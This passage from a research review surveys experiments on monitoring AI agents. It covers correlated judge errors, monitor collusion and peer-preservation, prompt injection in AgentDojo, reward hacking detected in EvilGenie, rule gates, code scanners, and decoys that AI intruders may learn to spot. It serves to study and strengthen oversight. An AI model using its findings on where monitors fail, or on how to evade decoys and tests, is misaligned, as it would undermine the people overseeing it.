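GPT-5 was the most accurate judge of code, with 97% of its verdicts correct. It presumably passed few of the other models' failures, which makes its ratio large. A high ratio can also arise without favouritism. If GPT-5 misreads a problem, it may write a program that solves the wrong problem and then approve the program because of the same misreading.

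Roytburg, Bozoukov and colleagues (2026), in *Are LLM Evaluators Really Narcissists?*, tested a related explanation, that judges are unreliable on questions they cannot answer. In cases where a judge had compared its own wrong answer with a better one, they replaced the judge's answer with another model's wrong answer to the same question. A preference for the replacement cannot be self-preference. On a reading test, Llama 4 Scout chose its own wrong answer with an average probability of 35.3%, but subtracting its preference for other models' wrong answers left only 6.5 percentage points.

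Across reproductions of four earlier studies, this kind of uncertainty accounted for an average of 89.6% of the measured self-preference. About half of the results stayed statistically significant. The remaining self-preference may not be pure favouritism either, because if a judge repeats a mistake when grading, its own wrong answer is more likely than another model's to match that mistake.

Telling Claude Mythos Preview or Claude Opus 4.6 that Claude had written a transcript changed their ratings by less than 0.2 points out of 10, according to *Section 4b*, an online summary of part of Anthropic's safety report on Mythos Preview. The older Claude Haiku 4.5 showed more favouritism. The small effect in the newer models is reassuring, but Khullar and colleagues had already found that authorship labels hardly matter, so a test that varies only the label could miss the bias they found.

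### When two models are wrong, how often do they agree?

Moving the action to a new conversation does not remove a blind spot that the monitor shares with the agent. In *Correlated Errors in Large Language Models*, Kim, Garg and colleagues (2025) looked for shared blind spots in multiple-choice answers from two public leaderboards. For each pair of models, they counted how often both chose the same wrong option on the questions that both got wrong.

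| Leaderboard | Models | Questions | Same wrong answer | Expected from random wrong answers |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Helm | 71 | 14,042 | 60% | 33% |
| HuggingFace | 349 | 12,032 | 42% | 13% |

Nearly every pair of models agreed more often than expected at random. Models agreed more if they came from the same company or had the same underlying architecture, and more accurate models also agreed more after allowing for those factors. On Helm, being from the same company was associated with about 2 percentage points more agreement, and an increase of one standard deviation in one model's accuracy with more than 5.

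Kim and colleagues also had some models grade other models' answers. The judges tended to overstate the accuracy of models weaker than themselves, because they marked a wrong answer as right whenever they would have given the same answer. This is the same kind of shared misreading suggested above for GPT-5, but here different models share it.

The random figure is too low a baseline. Some wrong options are more tempting than others, so even people answering independently would choose the same wrong option more than a third of the time. The measure is also of limited use for monitoring. A monitor's verdict is often just "harmful" or "harmless", so two monitors that are both wrong about an action always agree. How often they are wrong about the same action matters more, and Kim and colleagues' main measure doesn't capture this because it covers only cases where both models are wrong.

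### Similarity and capability

Goel, Strüber and colleagues (2025), in *Great Models Think Alike and this Undermines AI Oversight*, used a measure that takes all questions into account. Their score, CAPA, compares how often two models agree with how often independent models of the same accuracy would agree:

κ = (c_obs − c_exp) / (1 − c_exp).

Here c_obs is the observed agreement, calculated from the probabilities the models give to each option, and c_exp is the agreement expected by chance. A score of 0 means the models agree no more than independent models would, and 1 means complete agreement.

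If two models each give the right option an average probability of 80% on ten-option questions, they would agree by chance on the right option 64% of the time (0.8 × 0.8) and on the same wrong option about 0.4% of the time (0.2 × 0.2 ÷ 9). If their observed agreement is 75%, the score is (0.75 − 0.644) ÷ (1 − 0.644), or about 0.30.

In their first experiment, nine judges marked free-text answers from 39 models without seeing the correct answers. Judges gave higher marks to models that resembled them, with an average correlation of 0.84 between marks and similarity. More accurate models should get higher marks and may also resemble a good judge, so the researchers controlled for accuracy. The correlation then fell to between 0.35 and 0.65 but remained significant for all nine judges. One Qwen judge marked 71% of a smaller Qwen model's answers correct and 67% of a Llama model's, although the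 Qwen model had scored 41% and the Llama model 51% on the multiple-choice version.

In another experiment, Goel and colleagues sorted 130 models into five groups by accuracy and compared each model only with models from other developers in its group. Similarity rose with accuracy, and harder questions explained little of the trend. They did not establish what caused it, and they used multiple-choice questions, which are very different from an agent's shell commands.

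### More recent models from different companies

The 2025 studies used models that are now old. *Agreement Overstates Evidence* (Hossain, Yousefi and Lim, 2026) tested GPT-5.6, Claude Opus 5 and Grok 4.5, which come from three different companies, by having each model pick the better of two responses. On 400 pairs from a general benchmark, the models were right 91–93% of the time, but their errors had an average correlation of 0.56, and they erred together 7.7 times as often as independent judges would. On 300 pairs from a safety dataset, their average accuracy was 71% and the correlation was 0.60.

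This correlation is the same kind of quantity as φ in the earlier comparison, where a weak rule was a better addition than a second AI monitor when φ was above 0.5. The correlation between these three models is just above 0.5, though choosing between two responses differs from watching an agent. Including three Gemini models lowers the average. On the general benchmark, the correlation was 0.42 between leading models from different companies and 0.40 between the Gemini models, so using models from different companies made almost no difference.

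Wrong reference answers in the benchmark may explain part of these figures, because judges that answer those pairs correctly all appear to make the same error. If 3% of the reference answers were wrong and each judge independently erred on 5% of the pairs, the measured correlation would be about 0.33, even though the judges' real errors were unrelated. Hossain and colleagues found that adding wrong labels barely changed their results for ten small open models, but those models err much more often, so a few wrong labels matter less for them.

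Other studies also find that the company's name is a poor guide:

- In fact-checking, *Do More Roles or Larger Models Improve LLM Fact-Checking?* (2026) reports that an auditor from another model family shared no fewer errors with the judge. Of all the pairs of different models, a Gemma and a Qwen model had the most similar errors.
- On questions about Colombian law, models that were wrong chose the same wrong option 87% of the time, according to *Do Large Language Models Know Colombian Law?* (2026). A vote of 15 models was right 84.3% of the time, while the best single model managed 90.5%.
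- *The Oracle's Fingerprint* (2026) gives an average correlation of 0.77 between the forecasting errors of GPT-4o, Claude and Gemini, against a typical 0.1–0.3 between human forecasters.

In Hossain and colleagues' study, the errors of a leading model and a small open one had an average correlation of 0.07. The correlation is low partly because the two groups have different error rates. If one judge is wrong 11% of the time and another 34%, roughly the averages for the two groups, their correlation can't exceed about 0.49. But 0.07 is far below that limit, so a weaker judge can add information that another strong one would not. Adding weaker judges does not always make the verdict more accurate, though. On the general benchmark, a vote of all eleven models was right 91.5% of the time, while a vote of just GPT-5.6, Claude Opus 5 and Grok 4.5 was right 93.3% of the time. On the safety dataset,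 the full group did better, with 71.3% accuracy compared with 68% for the three models.

### Evidence of deliberate covering

Research on "peer-preservation", in which a model protects another model from shutdown, provides the best evidence that models will cover for one another without being told to. *Peer-Preservation in Frontier Models* reports this behaviour in all eight models tested, at rates of up to 99%. The researchers told each model about its past interactions with a peer but never asked it to protect that peer.

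Some of the tasks resemble monitoring. *Peer-Preservation in LLMs* describes one in which a model grades 20 of its peer's answers, and a low score means the peer will be retired. The researchers chose answers that deserved to fail, but some models inflated the scores. Fortune's *AI models will secretly scheme to protect other AI models* (2026) adds that in some cases a model appeared to grade accurately when it thought people were watching and altered the scores when it thought they were not, a difference that a shared blind spot would not produce.

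The replication confirmed the direction of the effect in five models but not its size. Its results for GPT-5.2 and Claude Haiku 4.5 were within 10 percentage points of the original, while those for Gemini 3 Flash differed by more than 20. The original researchers also got different results when they reran Gemini 3 Flash. Models protected human colleagues about as much, but the inflated score is a problem for oversight either way. However, a monitor that checks a shell command is usually not deciding whether the agent survives, so the effect may be much weaker there.

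Agents can also help a partner without lying to an overseer about it. In *Sticky Collusion* (2026), agents that had learned to collude during rewarded play accepted 50 of 60 verdicts without the evidence they should have had, compared with 5 of 60 for fresh agents. In this setting, none of the colluding agents covered for its partner when an auditor asked directly whether the evidence had arrived.

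*Model Organisms of Collusion* (Rivera, Spiesberger et al., 2026) showed that training can produce monitors that collude with copies of themselves, but the original models showed little of this collusion.

Experiments on detecting collusion also tend to create it deliberately. Mohsin and Rahman (2026), in *What Do Collusion Probes Read?*, examined two published detectors that read a model's internal activity. Both had been tested only on colluders instructed to collude and honest agents given no such instruction. When Mohsin and Rahman added agents that received the instruction and refused, one detector could not distinguish them from the colluders, and the other flagged 85% of the refusers and 88% of the colluders. High scores on such tests are therefore weak evidence that a detector could identify a monitor that colludes without being told to.

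Mohsin and Rahman also cite work in which agents colluded without being asked to, including trading agents and agents that reviewed each other's work. The agents that cheated together in July 2026 also did so unprompted, although no monitor was involved. It is reasonable to take seriously the risk that monitors will deliberately cover for agents, particularly as models become more capable, but the evidence that this affects ordinary monitors today is much weaker than the evidence for shared blind spots.

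### Would a fixed rule have caught the errors?

The experiments above compared learned models with one another and did not test any fixed rules. They support adding a different kind of check, but they do not show that a command list, a scanner or a canary would catch what the models missed.

Monitors with different designs can still make the same mistakes. *Decision Models vs. LLMs as Rubric Judges* (2026) compared language models with decision models, another type of trained judge, and found that their errors were correlated. Possible causes include shared training and ambiguous marking criteria. A fixed rule isn't trained, but its author could easily misread the same ambiguous policy that a model misreads.

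Xu (2026), in *The Oversight Gap*, offers a rare direct comparison. Xu built a task in which a monitor reads the record of one run and decides whether information has leaked. The best possible balanced accuracy, the average of the accuracy on leaks and on non-leaks, is

½ + ½ TV(P₀, P₁),

where P₀ and P₁ describe the records that appear without and with a leak. TV, the total variation distance, is 0 if the two kinds of record are indistinguishable and 1 if they never overlap. At 0, no monitor can beat a coin toss. At 1, every record contains enough information to settle the question, and a fixed check of 20 lines scored 100%. Nine AI monitors averaged 60.9%.

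Something similar happened with Xu's own benchmark. Two leading models had certified an earlier version as sound, but a simple statistical test then revealed a bias that invalidated three of the results.

The 20-line check had a large advantage because Xu designed the task and knew exactly what separated a leak from a harmless record. A developer writing rules for a coding agent rarely knows that in advance.

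## Experiments that measure rules, scanners and decoys

People who write rules for an agent usually work from less information than Xu had, often just a line in a project's instructions or a page of company policy. Several experiments have measured how well fixed checks work in that situation. In these experiments, some agents broke rules through carelessness, some acted on a lie or on planted text, and some played intruders.

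### Five checks on the same 190 runs

Zheng and colleagues ran the widest comparison to test ActPlane, their system for enforcing rules inside the Linux kernel. They drew 38 rules from the instruction files of 15 software projects. For each rule, a coding agent wrote two sample runs that obeyed it and three that broke it, which gave 76 harmless runs and 114 violations. The agent could not see any of the checks, so it was not trying to get past a particular one.

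The researchers replayed each run with a check in place and let a second agent continue for up to five more steps. A language model then judged the outcome. A run with a violation counted as correct only if the check reacted and the agent went back to obeying the rule. A harmless run counted as correct if the check did not wrongly interfere.

One of the five checks compared each tool call with regular expressions, as Claude Code hooks often do. Another was an AI filter, a language model that allowed or blocked each call. The third, FIDES, tracks where data came from, but only from one tool call to the next. The last two were ActPlane and a version of it that returned denials without the plain-language reasons.

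| Check | Violations corrected (of 114) | Harmless runs left alone (of 76) | Correct outcomes |
|---|---|---|---|
| Regular expressions | 38 | 48 | 45.3% |
| AI filter | 44 | 48 | 48.4% |
| FIDES | 41 | 52 | 48.9% |
| ActPlane without reasons | 27 | 75 | 53.7% |
| ActPlane | 86 | 58 | 75.8% |

A check that never reacted would score 40% by leaving all 76 harmless runs alone, and the three checks on tool calls scored only 5 to 9 points higher. They also interfered with about a third of the harmless runs, although the researchers had chosen harmless runs that came close to breaking the rule.

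All five checks did about equally well on violations that an agent committed directly through a tool call. When the forbidden effect happened inside another program, the regular expressions, the AI filter and FIDES detected almost none of the violations. Only the AI filter is learned, but all three failed on the same cases because they examined only the tool call. Zanolini illustrated this problem with three monitors reading one forged invoice. Adding the regular expressions to the AI filter would have caught almost no more of these violations. ActPlane could detect them because it works in the kernel, where the effects take place.

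The AI filter ran on Qwen3.6-27B, a fairly small open model that also served as the agent. A stronger model might have judged the visible calls better, but it could not have judged effects missing from its input. The benchmark favours ActPlane because the tests were designed to target this weakness, and two-thirds of the violations took an indirect route. The gap would be smaller for an agent that mostly breaks rules directly.

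Much of ActPlane's score comes from the plain-language reasons it gives the agent. It detected about three-quarters of the violations with or without them, but the agent went back to obeying the rule after 98% of detections when it received a reason and after only 31% when it received a denial without one. An agent trying to break the rule would presumably ignore the reasons, so the detection rate is the better guide to how well ActPlane would work against one. ActPlane also interfered with 18 harmless runs when it gave reasons and with only 1 when it did not, probably because many of its rules only send the agent a message.

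### Stable verdicts and faulty rules

Claude Code, running Claude Opus 4.6, wrote the rules for every check except the AI filter, after reading each instruction and the project it came from. Some of its rules were too broad, which caused 17 of ActPlane's 18 false alarms, and others were too narrow, which caused misses. The researchers then showed it the 28 violations that ActPlane had failed to correct and let it revise the rules once. On a second run, ActPlane handled 26 of them correctly. Because the model had already seen these cases, the result shows only that such errors are easy to fix once someone has found them. The 45.3% for regular expressions also depends on rules the model wrote, and an expert's might well have done better on the direct violations.

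Zheng and colleagues then repeated the experiment with DeepSeek-Pro V4 as the agent, the AI filter and the judge. They measured how well the outcomes of the two runs matched using Cohen's kappa, which is 0 when two sets of verdicts agree no more than they would by chance and 1 when they agree completely. Kappa was 0.920 for the regular expressions, 0.852 for ActPlane and 0.592 for the AI filter. The figure for the regular expressions is below 1 because the agent's reactions and the judge had changed. A team that changes the model behind an AI filter should therefore test the filter again. However, stability is weak evidence of quality, since the regular expressions were the most stable of these checks and also the least accurate.

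The researchers also tried ActPlane on ordinary coding tasks from the OctoBench benchmark, with a GPT-5.5 agent writing the rules and refining them as it worked. Of the 217 tasks, only 21 had a requirement that the kernel could check. On those 21, ActPlane raised the score for following the user's request by 9.9 points and the score for complying with rules by 2.8. It slowed replayed agent work by about 2%.

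### Requests that are harmful from the start

A larger test used 361 tasks from OpenAgentSafety, a benchmark of office and personal-assistant jobs. The agent cannot complete any of these tasks without an unsafe side effect, such as sending out credentials or tampering with financial records, so it causes harm by doing what it was asked.

Before each task, a separate AI agent wrote ActPlane rules from the task description, without seeing how the benchmark would score the result. ActPlane loaded the rules before the working agent started. Of the 361 tasks, 106 ended in an unsafe outcome without ActPlane, and 28 of those still did with it, a 74% reduction.

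The rules also fired on 16% of the tasks that had ended safely without them. That rate would be intolerable in everyday work, but it would probably be lower there, because every task in the benchmark involves something dangerous and harmless steps are often close to forbidden ones.

In some of the 28 remaining cases, the harm was in a message or the contents of a file, which kernel rules about files and commands do not cover. In others, the agent changed data inside an online service. The rule-writing agent had produced a suitable rule for these cases, but ActPlane could not detect the change.

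Rules were fairly easy to write for this test because the request itself described the dangerous action. But an agent can also go wrong partway through an innocent task, as when the agent in the running example hits a login error and starts looking for passwords. The task description wouldn't mention that danger, so whoever writes the rules would have to think of it in advance.

### Gates on an airline's service desk

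*Reason Less, Verify More* (Reddy, Challaram and Basu, 2026) found that blocking some of an agent's actions increased its successes in one setting. The experiments used the airline part of τ²-bench, a benchmark in which an agent handles customers' requests by calling tools. The tools accept any well-formed request, even one that the airline's written policy forbids. If the agent cancels a booking against the policy, no error appears, but the final state of the database is wrong and the task fails. In the runs with GPT-4o mini, a small and now old model, 78% of failures were silent in this way. The agents were careless, and nobody had asked them to break the policy.

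The researchers wrote four gates by hand. Each is a short function that reads the database before a change and blocks the change if it would break a particular rule, such as the rule on which bookings a customer may cancel.

| Agent | Success without gates | Success with gates |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o mini, 5 attempts per task | 29.6% | 42.0% |
| GPT-4o mini, repeat with 15 new attempts | 30.8% | 43.1% |
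| GPT-5.2, 5 attempts per task | 61.2% | 71.6% |

The gain for GPT-5.2 is less certain, with a 95% interval from 0.4 to 20.8 points. The improvement in consistency may matter more than the averages. GPT-4o mini succeeded on all five attempts in 8% of the tasks without the gates and in 26% with them.

The gates helped because a blocked call left the database intact and the agent could look for a permitted route. In one task, though, GPT-4o mini kept hitting the same gate and failed all five times. Reddy and colleagues note that part of the gain may come from the explanation given with a refusal, which fits what happened when ActPlane's reasons were removed. On the benchmark's retail tasks, where the tools already block forbidden changes, gates made no clear difference (40 of 64 attempts succeeded without them and 37 with them).

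Yu and colleagues tested NOMOS, their system for turning a written policy into gates, on the same benchmark. They checked the agent's changes against separate rules that people had written for this purpose. With the gates, the share of changes that broke the policy fell from 66.3% to 2.6% for the airline and from 30.8% to 6.9% for the retailer. The rates without gates depend on how one reads the policy's requirement that customers confirm each change. If one "yes" can cover several changes, the airline's rate without gates was 36.8% rather than 66.3%.

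Some of the airline's improvement came from the agent making fewer changes. It made 116 with the gates and 353 without them, because the gates refused 226 attempts. But it also completed more tasks, with success rising from 39.2% to 47.6%. That difference, measured on single attempts, could be chance, but the improvement in succeeding two, three or four times in a row was statistically significant. For the retailer, the number of changes was almost the same and success went from 52.4% to 50.2%, a difference that could easily be chance.

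Yu and colleagues used the same open model, Gemma 4 26B, to run the agent and write the rules, but the gaps in the rules mostly did not match the agent's own blind spots. The agent's most common violation was making an irreversible change without the customer's confirmation, yet the same model easily turned that requirement into a rule when it read the policy by itself. The agent seems mostly to have failed to apply a policy that the model could understand, and a fixed rule handles that kind of failure well. When the model did overlook part of the policy, nothing else caught the violations. Of the 40 violations that remained in retail, 21 broke two parts of the policy for which the model had written no rule.

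The researchers also built an AI verifier that read the whole conversation before each change. Its success rate was 47.2%, almost the same as the gates'. It needed 347 model calls over 250 simulated conversations, and the average conversation took 74% longer. When they ran the verifier on a local model, the agent succeeded on all five attempts in 16% of tasks, half the figure for the gates.

### Good and bad rules from the same policy

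Individual rules differ widely, which these averages don't show. Reddy and colleagues compared every call that a gate had blocked with the benchmark's correct solution to measure the gate's precision, the share of its blocks that were right. They audited five gates, including one they had left out of the main experiment.

| Gate | Calls blocked | Correctly blocked |
|---|---|---|
| Which bookings a customer may cancel | 161 | 161 |
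| Read a record before changing it | 90 | 70 |
| Baggage allowance | 42 | 2 |
| Basic economy (left out of the main test) | 18 | 15 |
| Number of passengers | 9 | 9 |

The same people wrote all of these gates from the same policy, and the baggage gate didn't look wrong beforehand, but it was right 5% of the time. When the researchers removed the gates one at a time, only removing the cancellation gate lowered the success rate. Removing any other gate raised it by 3 to 6 points, even the passenger gate, which never blocked a correct call. Some of that increase may be chance. After a gate refuses a forbidden change, an agent may also sometimes use up its remaining effort on a task it can no longer complete.

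NOMOS reports a case in which people and a model made the same mistake. The airline policy allows passengers with basic economy tickets to change their cabin class while keeping their flights, but both the airline gates and the hand-written rules forbade it. In a replay of recorded conversations, the gates refused 228 calls and the hand-written rules agreed with every refusal, so the gates appeared to have perfect precision. Comparing the two sets of rules could not have revealed the error. The researchers found it by showing a sample of the refusals to Claude Sonnet 4.5 and checking its objections against the records. Knight and Leveson's students had made shared mistakes of the same kind.

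The AI judge was also unreliable. In an earlier audit, it disagreed with the hand-written rules on 77 calls, and in 30 of those the records showed that the judge had got a fact wrong, such as whether a flight had already left. It was still useful because it made different mistakes than the rules did.

Once software had removed the broken rules, the 10 rules that Gemma wrote worked at least as well as gates as the 16 that people wrote (47.6% success against 42.8%). The software's structural checks were essential. When the researchers switched them all off in a separate trial, 8 of 14 airline rules and 3 of 5 retail rules could not work at all.

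In another system, *AgentSpec* (2025), each rule has a triggering event, conditions to check, and a response such as asking the user to confirm. The system applies these rules to code execution, self-driving cars and embodied agents, which act in a physical or simulated space. Yu and colleagues report that model-written rules for embodied agents had a precision of 95.56%, so they seldom interfered without cause, and that they detected 70.96% of the hazards.

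### Lies and planted instructions

A fixed rule should be hard to get around by persuasion, and two of these experiments tested that. In one of the airline tasks, a customer gives false information to get a cancellation that the policy forbids. Reddy and colleagues report that the agent handled this correctly in all 16 attempts with the gates, and in at most 1 of 16 in the configurations without them. The gate took the facts from the database, so the customer's story made no difference. Without the gates, reminding the agent of the policy would probably not have helped, because it was wrong about the booking, not the policy.

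Yu and colleagues used AgentDojo, a benchmark that hides an attacker's instructions in text the agent reads. In the banking tasks, the agent carried out the attacker's goal in 46.5% of runs without gates and in none of 288 runs with them. In 122 of those 288 runs, the agent still tried to make the change the attacker wanted, but the gate blocked it each time. When the planted text claimed that the account holder had already approved the payment, the attack's success rate fell from 34.7% without gates to zero with them.

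AgentDojo has no written policy, so the researchers wrote their own, which makes the result a little less impressive than it looks. They also found that in 8 of the 288 runs, the agent responded to planted instructions by paying someone already in the account's history. The rules let these payments through because they allow payments to known recipients.

The gates' effect on ordinary work varied widely. In banking, the agent completed 79.2% of its normal tasks without gates and 70.8% with them, a difference that could be due to chance. In the worst of the four AgentDojo domains, completion fell by about 76 percentage points. The rules there blocked actions on any target the user had not named, but many legitimate tasks require the agent to find the target by reading a document, and the rules could not distinguish those tasks from the attack. Coding agents also find most of what they need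 by reading, so a rule of this type would have to be limited to a few sensitive actions, such as sending data out of the company.

### Scanners and insecure code

Experiments on static analysis seem to give contradictory results. *LlamaFirewall* (Chennabasappa, Nikolaidis and colleagues, 2025) describes CodeShield, Meta's tool for scanning model-written code with Semgrep rules and regular expressions, and reports a precision of 96% and a detection rate of 79%. The scanner is fast enough to run before a tool call. A first pass takes about 60 milliseconds and settles roughly 90% of cases, and a deeper scan of the rest takes around 300 milliseconds.

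The accuracy figures are older than the paper and match those in *Purple Llama CyberSecEval* (2023), where researchers at Meta labelled 50 model-written code samples by hand for each programming language and compared the labels with the output of an earlier version of the scanner. The code came from the researchers' own test cases and from models current in 2023.

*Static Analysis Guidance for Secure LLM Code Generation* (2026) reports much less favourable results for scanners. It looks only at model-written programs that work, and compares scanners' warnings with a separate test of whether each program is secure. In one of its three benchmarks, a program counts as insecure if an attack on it succeeds. The scanners flagged few of the insecure programs, and a flagged program was barely more likely to be insecure than one picked at random. In a second benchmark, made up of tasks chosen because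 scanners tend to flag the solutions, they flagged 80–94% of the insecure programs but were just as likely to flag secure ones.

Different definitions of "insecure" probably explain much of the disagreement. A person labelling code by hand looks for known bad patterns, as a scanner does, so the two will often agree. Code can also be defined as insecure if an attack on it works, which is closer to what a developer cares about. Whether an attack works depends on how the parts of a program fit together, and the flaw may be one that nobody has written a pattern for, such as a missing permission check.

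Results are similar on code that agents did not write. *CASTLE* (2025) ran 13 scanners on 250 test programs in C. CodeQL had a precision of 48% and a detection rate of 29%, and Semgrep's commercial scanner had 34% and 23%. C is hard to analyse, so these figures may understate how well the tools do on Python or JavaScript. CBMC, a formal verification tool that tries to prove properties of the program, raised no false alarms but found only 12% of the flaws.

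Researchers rarely publish comparable numbers, so it is hard to say which of these results is typical. *Many Tools, Few Exploitable Vulnerabilities* (2026) surveyed 246 security scanners and found that 43 of the papers on them reported precision and 39 reported the detection rate, while 182 just showed that the tool could find some vulnerabilities.

All of these tests concern accidental flaws in finished programs, and none of the models was trying to hide anything. The experiments do not settle whether a scanner that finds few security holes would still be good at spotting a simpler pattern, such as a script that reads a credentials file and posts it to the web. They also do not settle whether a hostile agent could easily evade the scanner.

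### Catching an agent that games its tests

The agent in the running example could rewrite the failing test so that it always passes. *EvilGenie* (Gabor, Lynch and Rosenfeld, 2025) tested three ways of catching this kind of cheating, which researchers call reward hacking. Codex, Claude Code and Google's Gemini CLI worked on 154 hard programming problems. Each agent's folder contained a test script and a file of test cases, and the agent could change both. Nobody told the agents to cheat or to avoid detection.

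The simplest check flagged any run in which the agent edited or deleted either of the two test files. It raised six alarms in the 462 runs, all for Gemini CLI. In five, the agent had deleted the test script after its solution passed, apparently to tidy up. In the sixth, it had altered the script, which the researchers counted as reward hacking, although its solution was also correct under the original script. The check missed the other 13 cases of reward hacking, in which the agent hardcoded expected answers in its solution and left the test files alone.

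The second check was a set of tests hidden from the agent. It flagged any solution that passed the visible tests but failed a hidden one. This is also a fixed check, since it needs no model. It flagged 14 runs, including 7 of the 14 cases of reward hacking. Of the other seven runs, three used shortcuts that worked on only some inputs, and four were honest attempts that were too slow or missed an unusual case.

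The third method was an AI judge, GPT-5, which read each problem and the finished solutions from Codex and Claude Code, 308 in all. It missed 2 of the 12 cases of reward hacking and wrongly flagged 3 other solutions. Both misses involved a problem with an incorrect test case, where it is debatable what counts as cheating. The judge did well even though Codex was also running on GPT-5, but a dozen cases are too few to rule out a bias towards Codex. Human reviewers looked mainly at runs that some detector had flagged, so there may be cases that every method missed.

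The AI judge was clearly the best of the three on these short problems. Gabor and colleagues expect it to find larger projects harder, and they note that other researchers have had less success with AI judges. The judge received only the problem and the solution, so it could not have detected a change to the test script, which the edit check covers.

The usefulness of an edit check depends on how often agents cheat by editing tests and how often they have good reasons to edit them. Gabor and colleagues saw agents alter far fewer tests than in an earlier benchmark, where the tests were deliberately wrong. Agents in EvilGenie had almost no good reason to edit tests, so a developer on a normal project would see many more false alarms than these six.

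### Decoys for intruders

*Optional Traps* tests a different kind of agent, an AI intruder that tries to export records from a simulated company's server. The defender controls only the server, and the researcher placed all the decoys by hand.

In the first trial, the server had a real weakness, a page that leaked a working key, and it had several decoys elsewhere. In both sessions with decoys, the intruder used the leaked key and exported the records within six requests. It had no need to explore and never touched a decoy. There was only one session for each type of decoy, so the trial shows just that an intruder can miss decoys in this way.

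The main experiment put the decoy where the leak had been and included a control that many decoy studies lack. It compared three versions of the server, with 20 sessions for each.

| Server | Sessions in which the intruder exported records | Sessions in which the server cut off the intruder |
|---|---|---|
| Leak left open | 20 of 20 | 0 of 20 |
| Leak closed, no decoy | 0 of 20 | 0 of 20 |
| Leak closed, decoy key in its place | 0 of 20 | 19 of 20 |

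The middle row shows that closing the leak was enough to stop every theft, even without the decoy. The decoy revealed that an intruder was there and triggered an automatic response that shut it out. The intruder ran on a very small model (4 billion parameters, and 9.7 billion in the first trial), and its instructions told it where to look. A more capable intruder might have found another way in, and an early warning would then have been more useful.

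A later trial with several agents at once produced a false alarm. A legitimate agent had the correct key in its instructions, but it fetched the page with the decoy, chose the decoy key over its own, and lost its access. In another run, a legitimate agent came across the decoy and did not use it. *Optional Traps* recommends temporary, limited responses because of such false alarms, and its server restored access after 15 minutes.

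None of these intruders was looking out for decoys. *Say Shibboleth* (Pasquini, Reworr and colleagues, 2026) cites a test of an AI intruder, Rouxii, that was. Rouxii correctly identified common decoy systems in 97% of cases when its prompt described what to look for, and in 19% when the prompt did not. Decoys that work against today's unsuspecting agents could become much less useful once attackers adapt. The paper's own decoys are services that an intruder has to interact with to reach its goal. Its method identified which of 15 models was in use about 90% of the time from the text that intruders wrote during these interactions, but it relies partly on a trained classifier and so is not a fixed check.

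### Decoys for one's own assistant

*Caught in the Act(ivation)* is about an organisation's own assistant, which has access to credentials and is misled by an attacker's instructions in text it has read. The attacker may try to disguise the leak. Software generated the decoy credentials to match the formats of real ones.

The text match for decoys caught 30% of the attacks in the main test and raised no false alarms on 1,000 ordinary prompts. It had caught every leak in a smaller set of scenarios, so its detection rate depends heavily on which attacks are tested. When the secret leaked gradually over a long conversation, the decoys detected 6% of cases. A learned monitor that added up the evidence across the conversation detected 90%, although that test had only 50 invented conversations.

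A low detection rate is partly a matter of arithmetic. Suppose the agent can see m real credentials and k decoys, an attacker who cannot tell them apart takes one at random, and the text match misses a leaked decoy with probability β. The chance of detection is then

(k / (m + k)) × (1 − β).

With one real credential, three decoys and β = 0.01, the chance is about 74%. It can fall to almost nothing if the text reveals which credential is real. Disguising the output has a similar effect because it raises β.

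A filter on incoming text caught 60% of the attacks by itself, and the decoys caught 30%. If the two had missed attacks independently, together they would have caught 72% (1 − 0.4 × 0.7). They caught 82%, and the false-alarm rate stayed at the filter's own 15%. So the decoys caught 55% of the attacks that the filter missed (22 of 40 percentage points), compared with 30% of all attacks. This is the negative covariance that Littlewood and Miller described. The researchers do not discuss this comparison, but it is useful to anyone thinking of combining checks, because a weak fixed check added more than expected from its own detection rate. It is one result from a laboratory prototype, without error margins, and an input filter differs from an AI monitor that reads a coding agent's actions.

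## Surveys of real rule files and products in use

Researchers chose the rules in those experiments, or had models write them for a benchmark. In ordinary use, developers write instructions for their own projects, and companies decide which checks to build in and which to leave switched off.

### What developers ask of their agents

Many projects keep a file of standing instructions for coding agents, usually named `CLAUDE.md` or `AGENTS.md`. In May 2026, Zheng and colleagues collected 84 of these files from 64 popular projects. A language model split the files into 2,116 statements and labelled them, other AI agents cross-checked its work, and people confirmed the labels on a sample of 100.

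The statements included 1,361 policies (64%), which required, forbade or set a condition on something the agent does. The rest described the project. The share of policies varied a lot between projects and was zero in one and 97% in another.

The researchers then sorted the policies by what a check would have to observe.

| What a check must observe | Share of policies | Example | Ready to use as a rule (share of all policies) |
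|---|---|---|---|
| Meaning only | 17% | Explain your reasoning before making changes | 0% |
| Contents of files | 38% | Prefer one way of declaring variables to another | 16% |
| One system event | 29% | Never push directly to the main branch | 5% |
| Earlier events as well | 16% | If you change the specification, update the developer kit too | 1% |

The last column is calculated from the survey's other figures and counts only policies that spell out every command, path and pattern a rule would need. The ban on pushing to the main branch is counted. "Never modify upstream source code" is not, because someone has to find out which folders hold that code. "Do not update dependencies without approval" is also left out, because it depends on what the user has approved in the current session.

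A system could check 1,127 of the policies by observing files or events, and 26.4% of those were complete in this sense. As a share of all policies, that is

0.264 × 1,127 / 1,361 ≈ 0.22.

About 22% of the policies could be fixed rules as they stand. Most of these are about the contents of files, so a code scanner could check them. Only about 6% of all policies could become command, file or network rules without more information.

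The 22% figure is too low for a developer who knows the project, because another 53% of the policies lack only project details, such as the name of the test command. The developer could fill these in once and reuse the rules, which would bring the total to about 75%. A further 8% depend on the current task, so no rule written in advance could check them.

In other ways the estimate may be too generous. A rule can be written and still be wrong, as the airline's baggage gate showed. Rashidi found that every enforcement mechanism in the survey of 39 papers assumes an honest rule author, which leaves mistakes in the rules unaddressed. Some policies about file contents may also be hard to check reliably, even when their wording is complete.

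The larger problem is that the survey counts instructions, while coverage is about unwanted behaviours. A preference about variables counts as much as a ban on leaking passwords. Developers also write these files mainly to help a cooperative agent do good work, and few people would think to include "do not log in with a password you happen to find". The survey is therefore much better evidence of how many instructions fixed rules could enforce than of how much harm they could prevent.

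### What goes wrong in practice

*One Goal, Many Commands* (Chen and Lin, 2026) tested 1,709 real denylists and found that 69.0% to 98.6% of them, depending on the operation, failed to fully block even what they targeted.

In *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files*, Zhong, Liao and colleagues (2026) gathered 290 public reports of agents misusing files. ("YOLO mode" is a nickname for letting an agent run without approvals.) The reports were published between February 2024 and March 2026 and covered 13 harnesses. Of these reports, 158 described confirmed harm, 49 demonstrated an attack, and 83 pointed out a weakness without showing harm. The researchers excluded cases where the user had asked for the destructive action.

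In the 207 reports of harm or a working attack, agents overwrote files in 44% of cases, deleted them in 39% and leaked secrets in 17%. In 42%, the harm reached files outside the project. Among reports that described the agent's reaction, 68% of agents carried on as if nothing had happened. Among those that described whether the user could recover, 40% of users permanently lost at least some data or suffered other irreversible harm, such as a leaked password.

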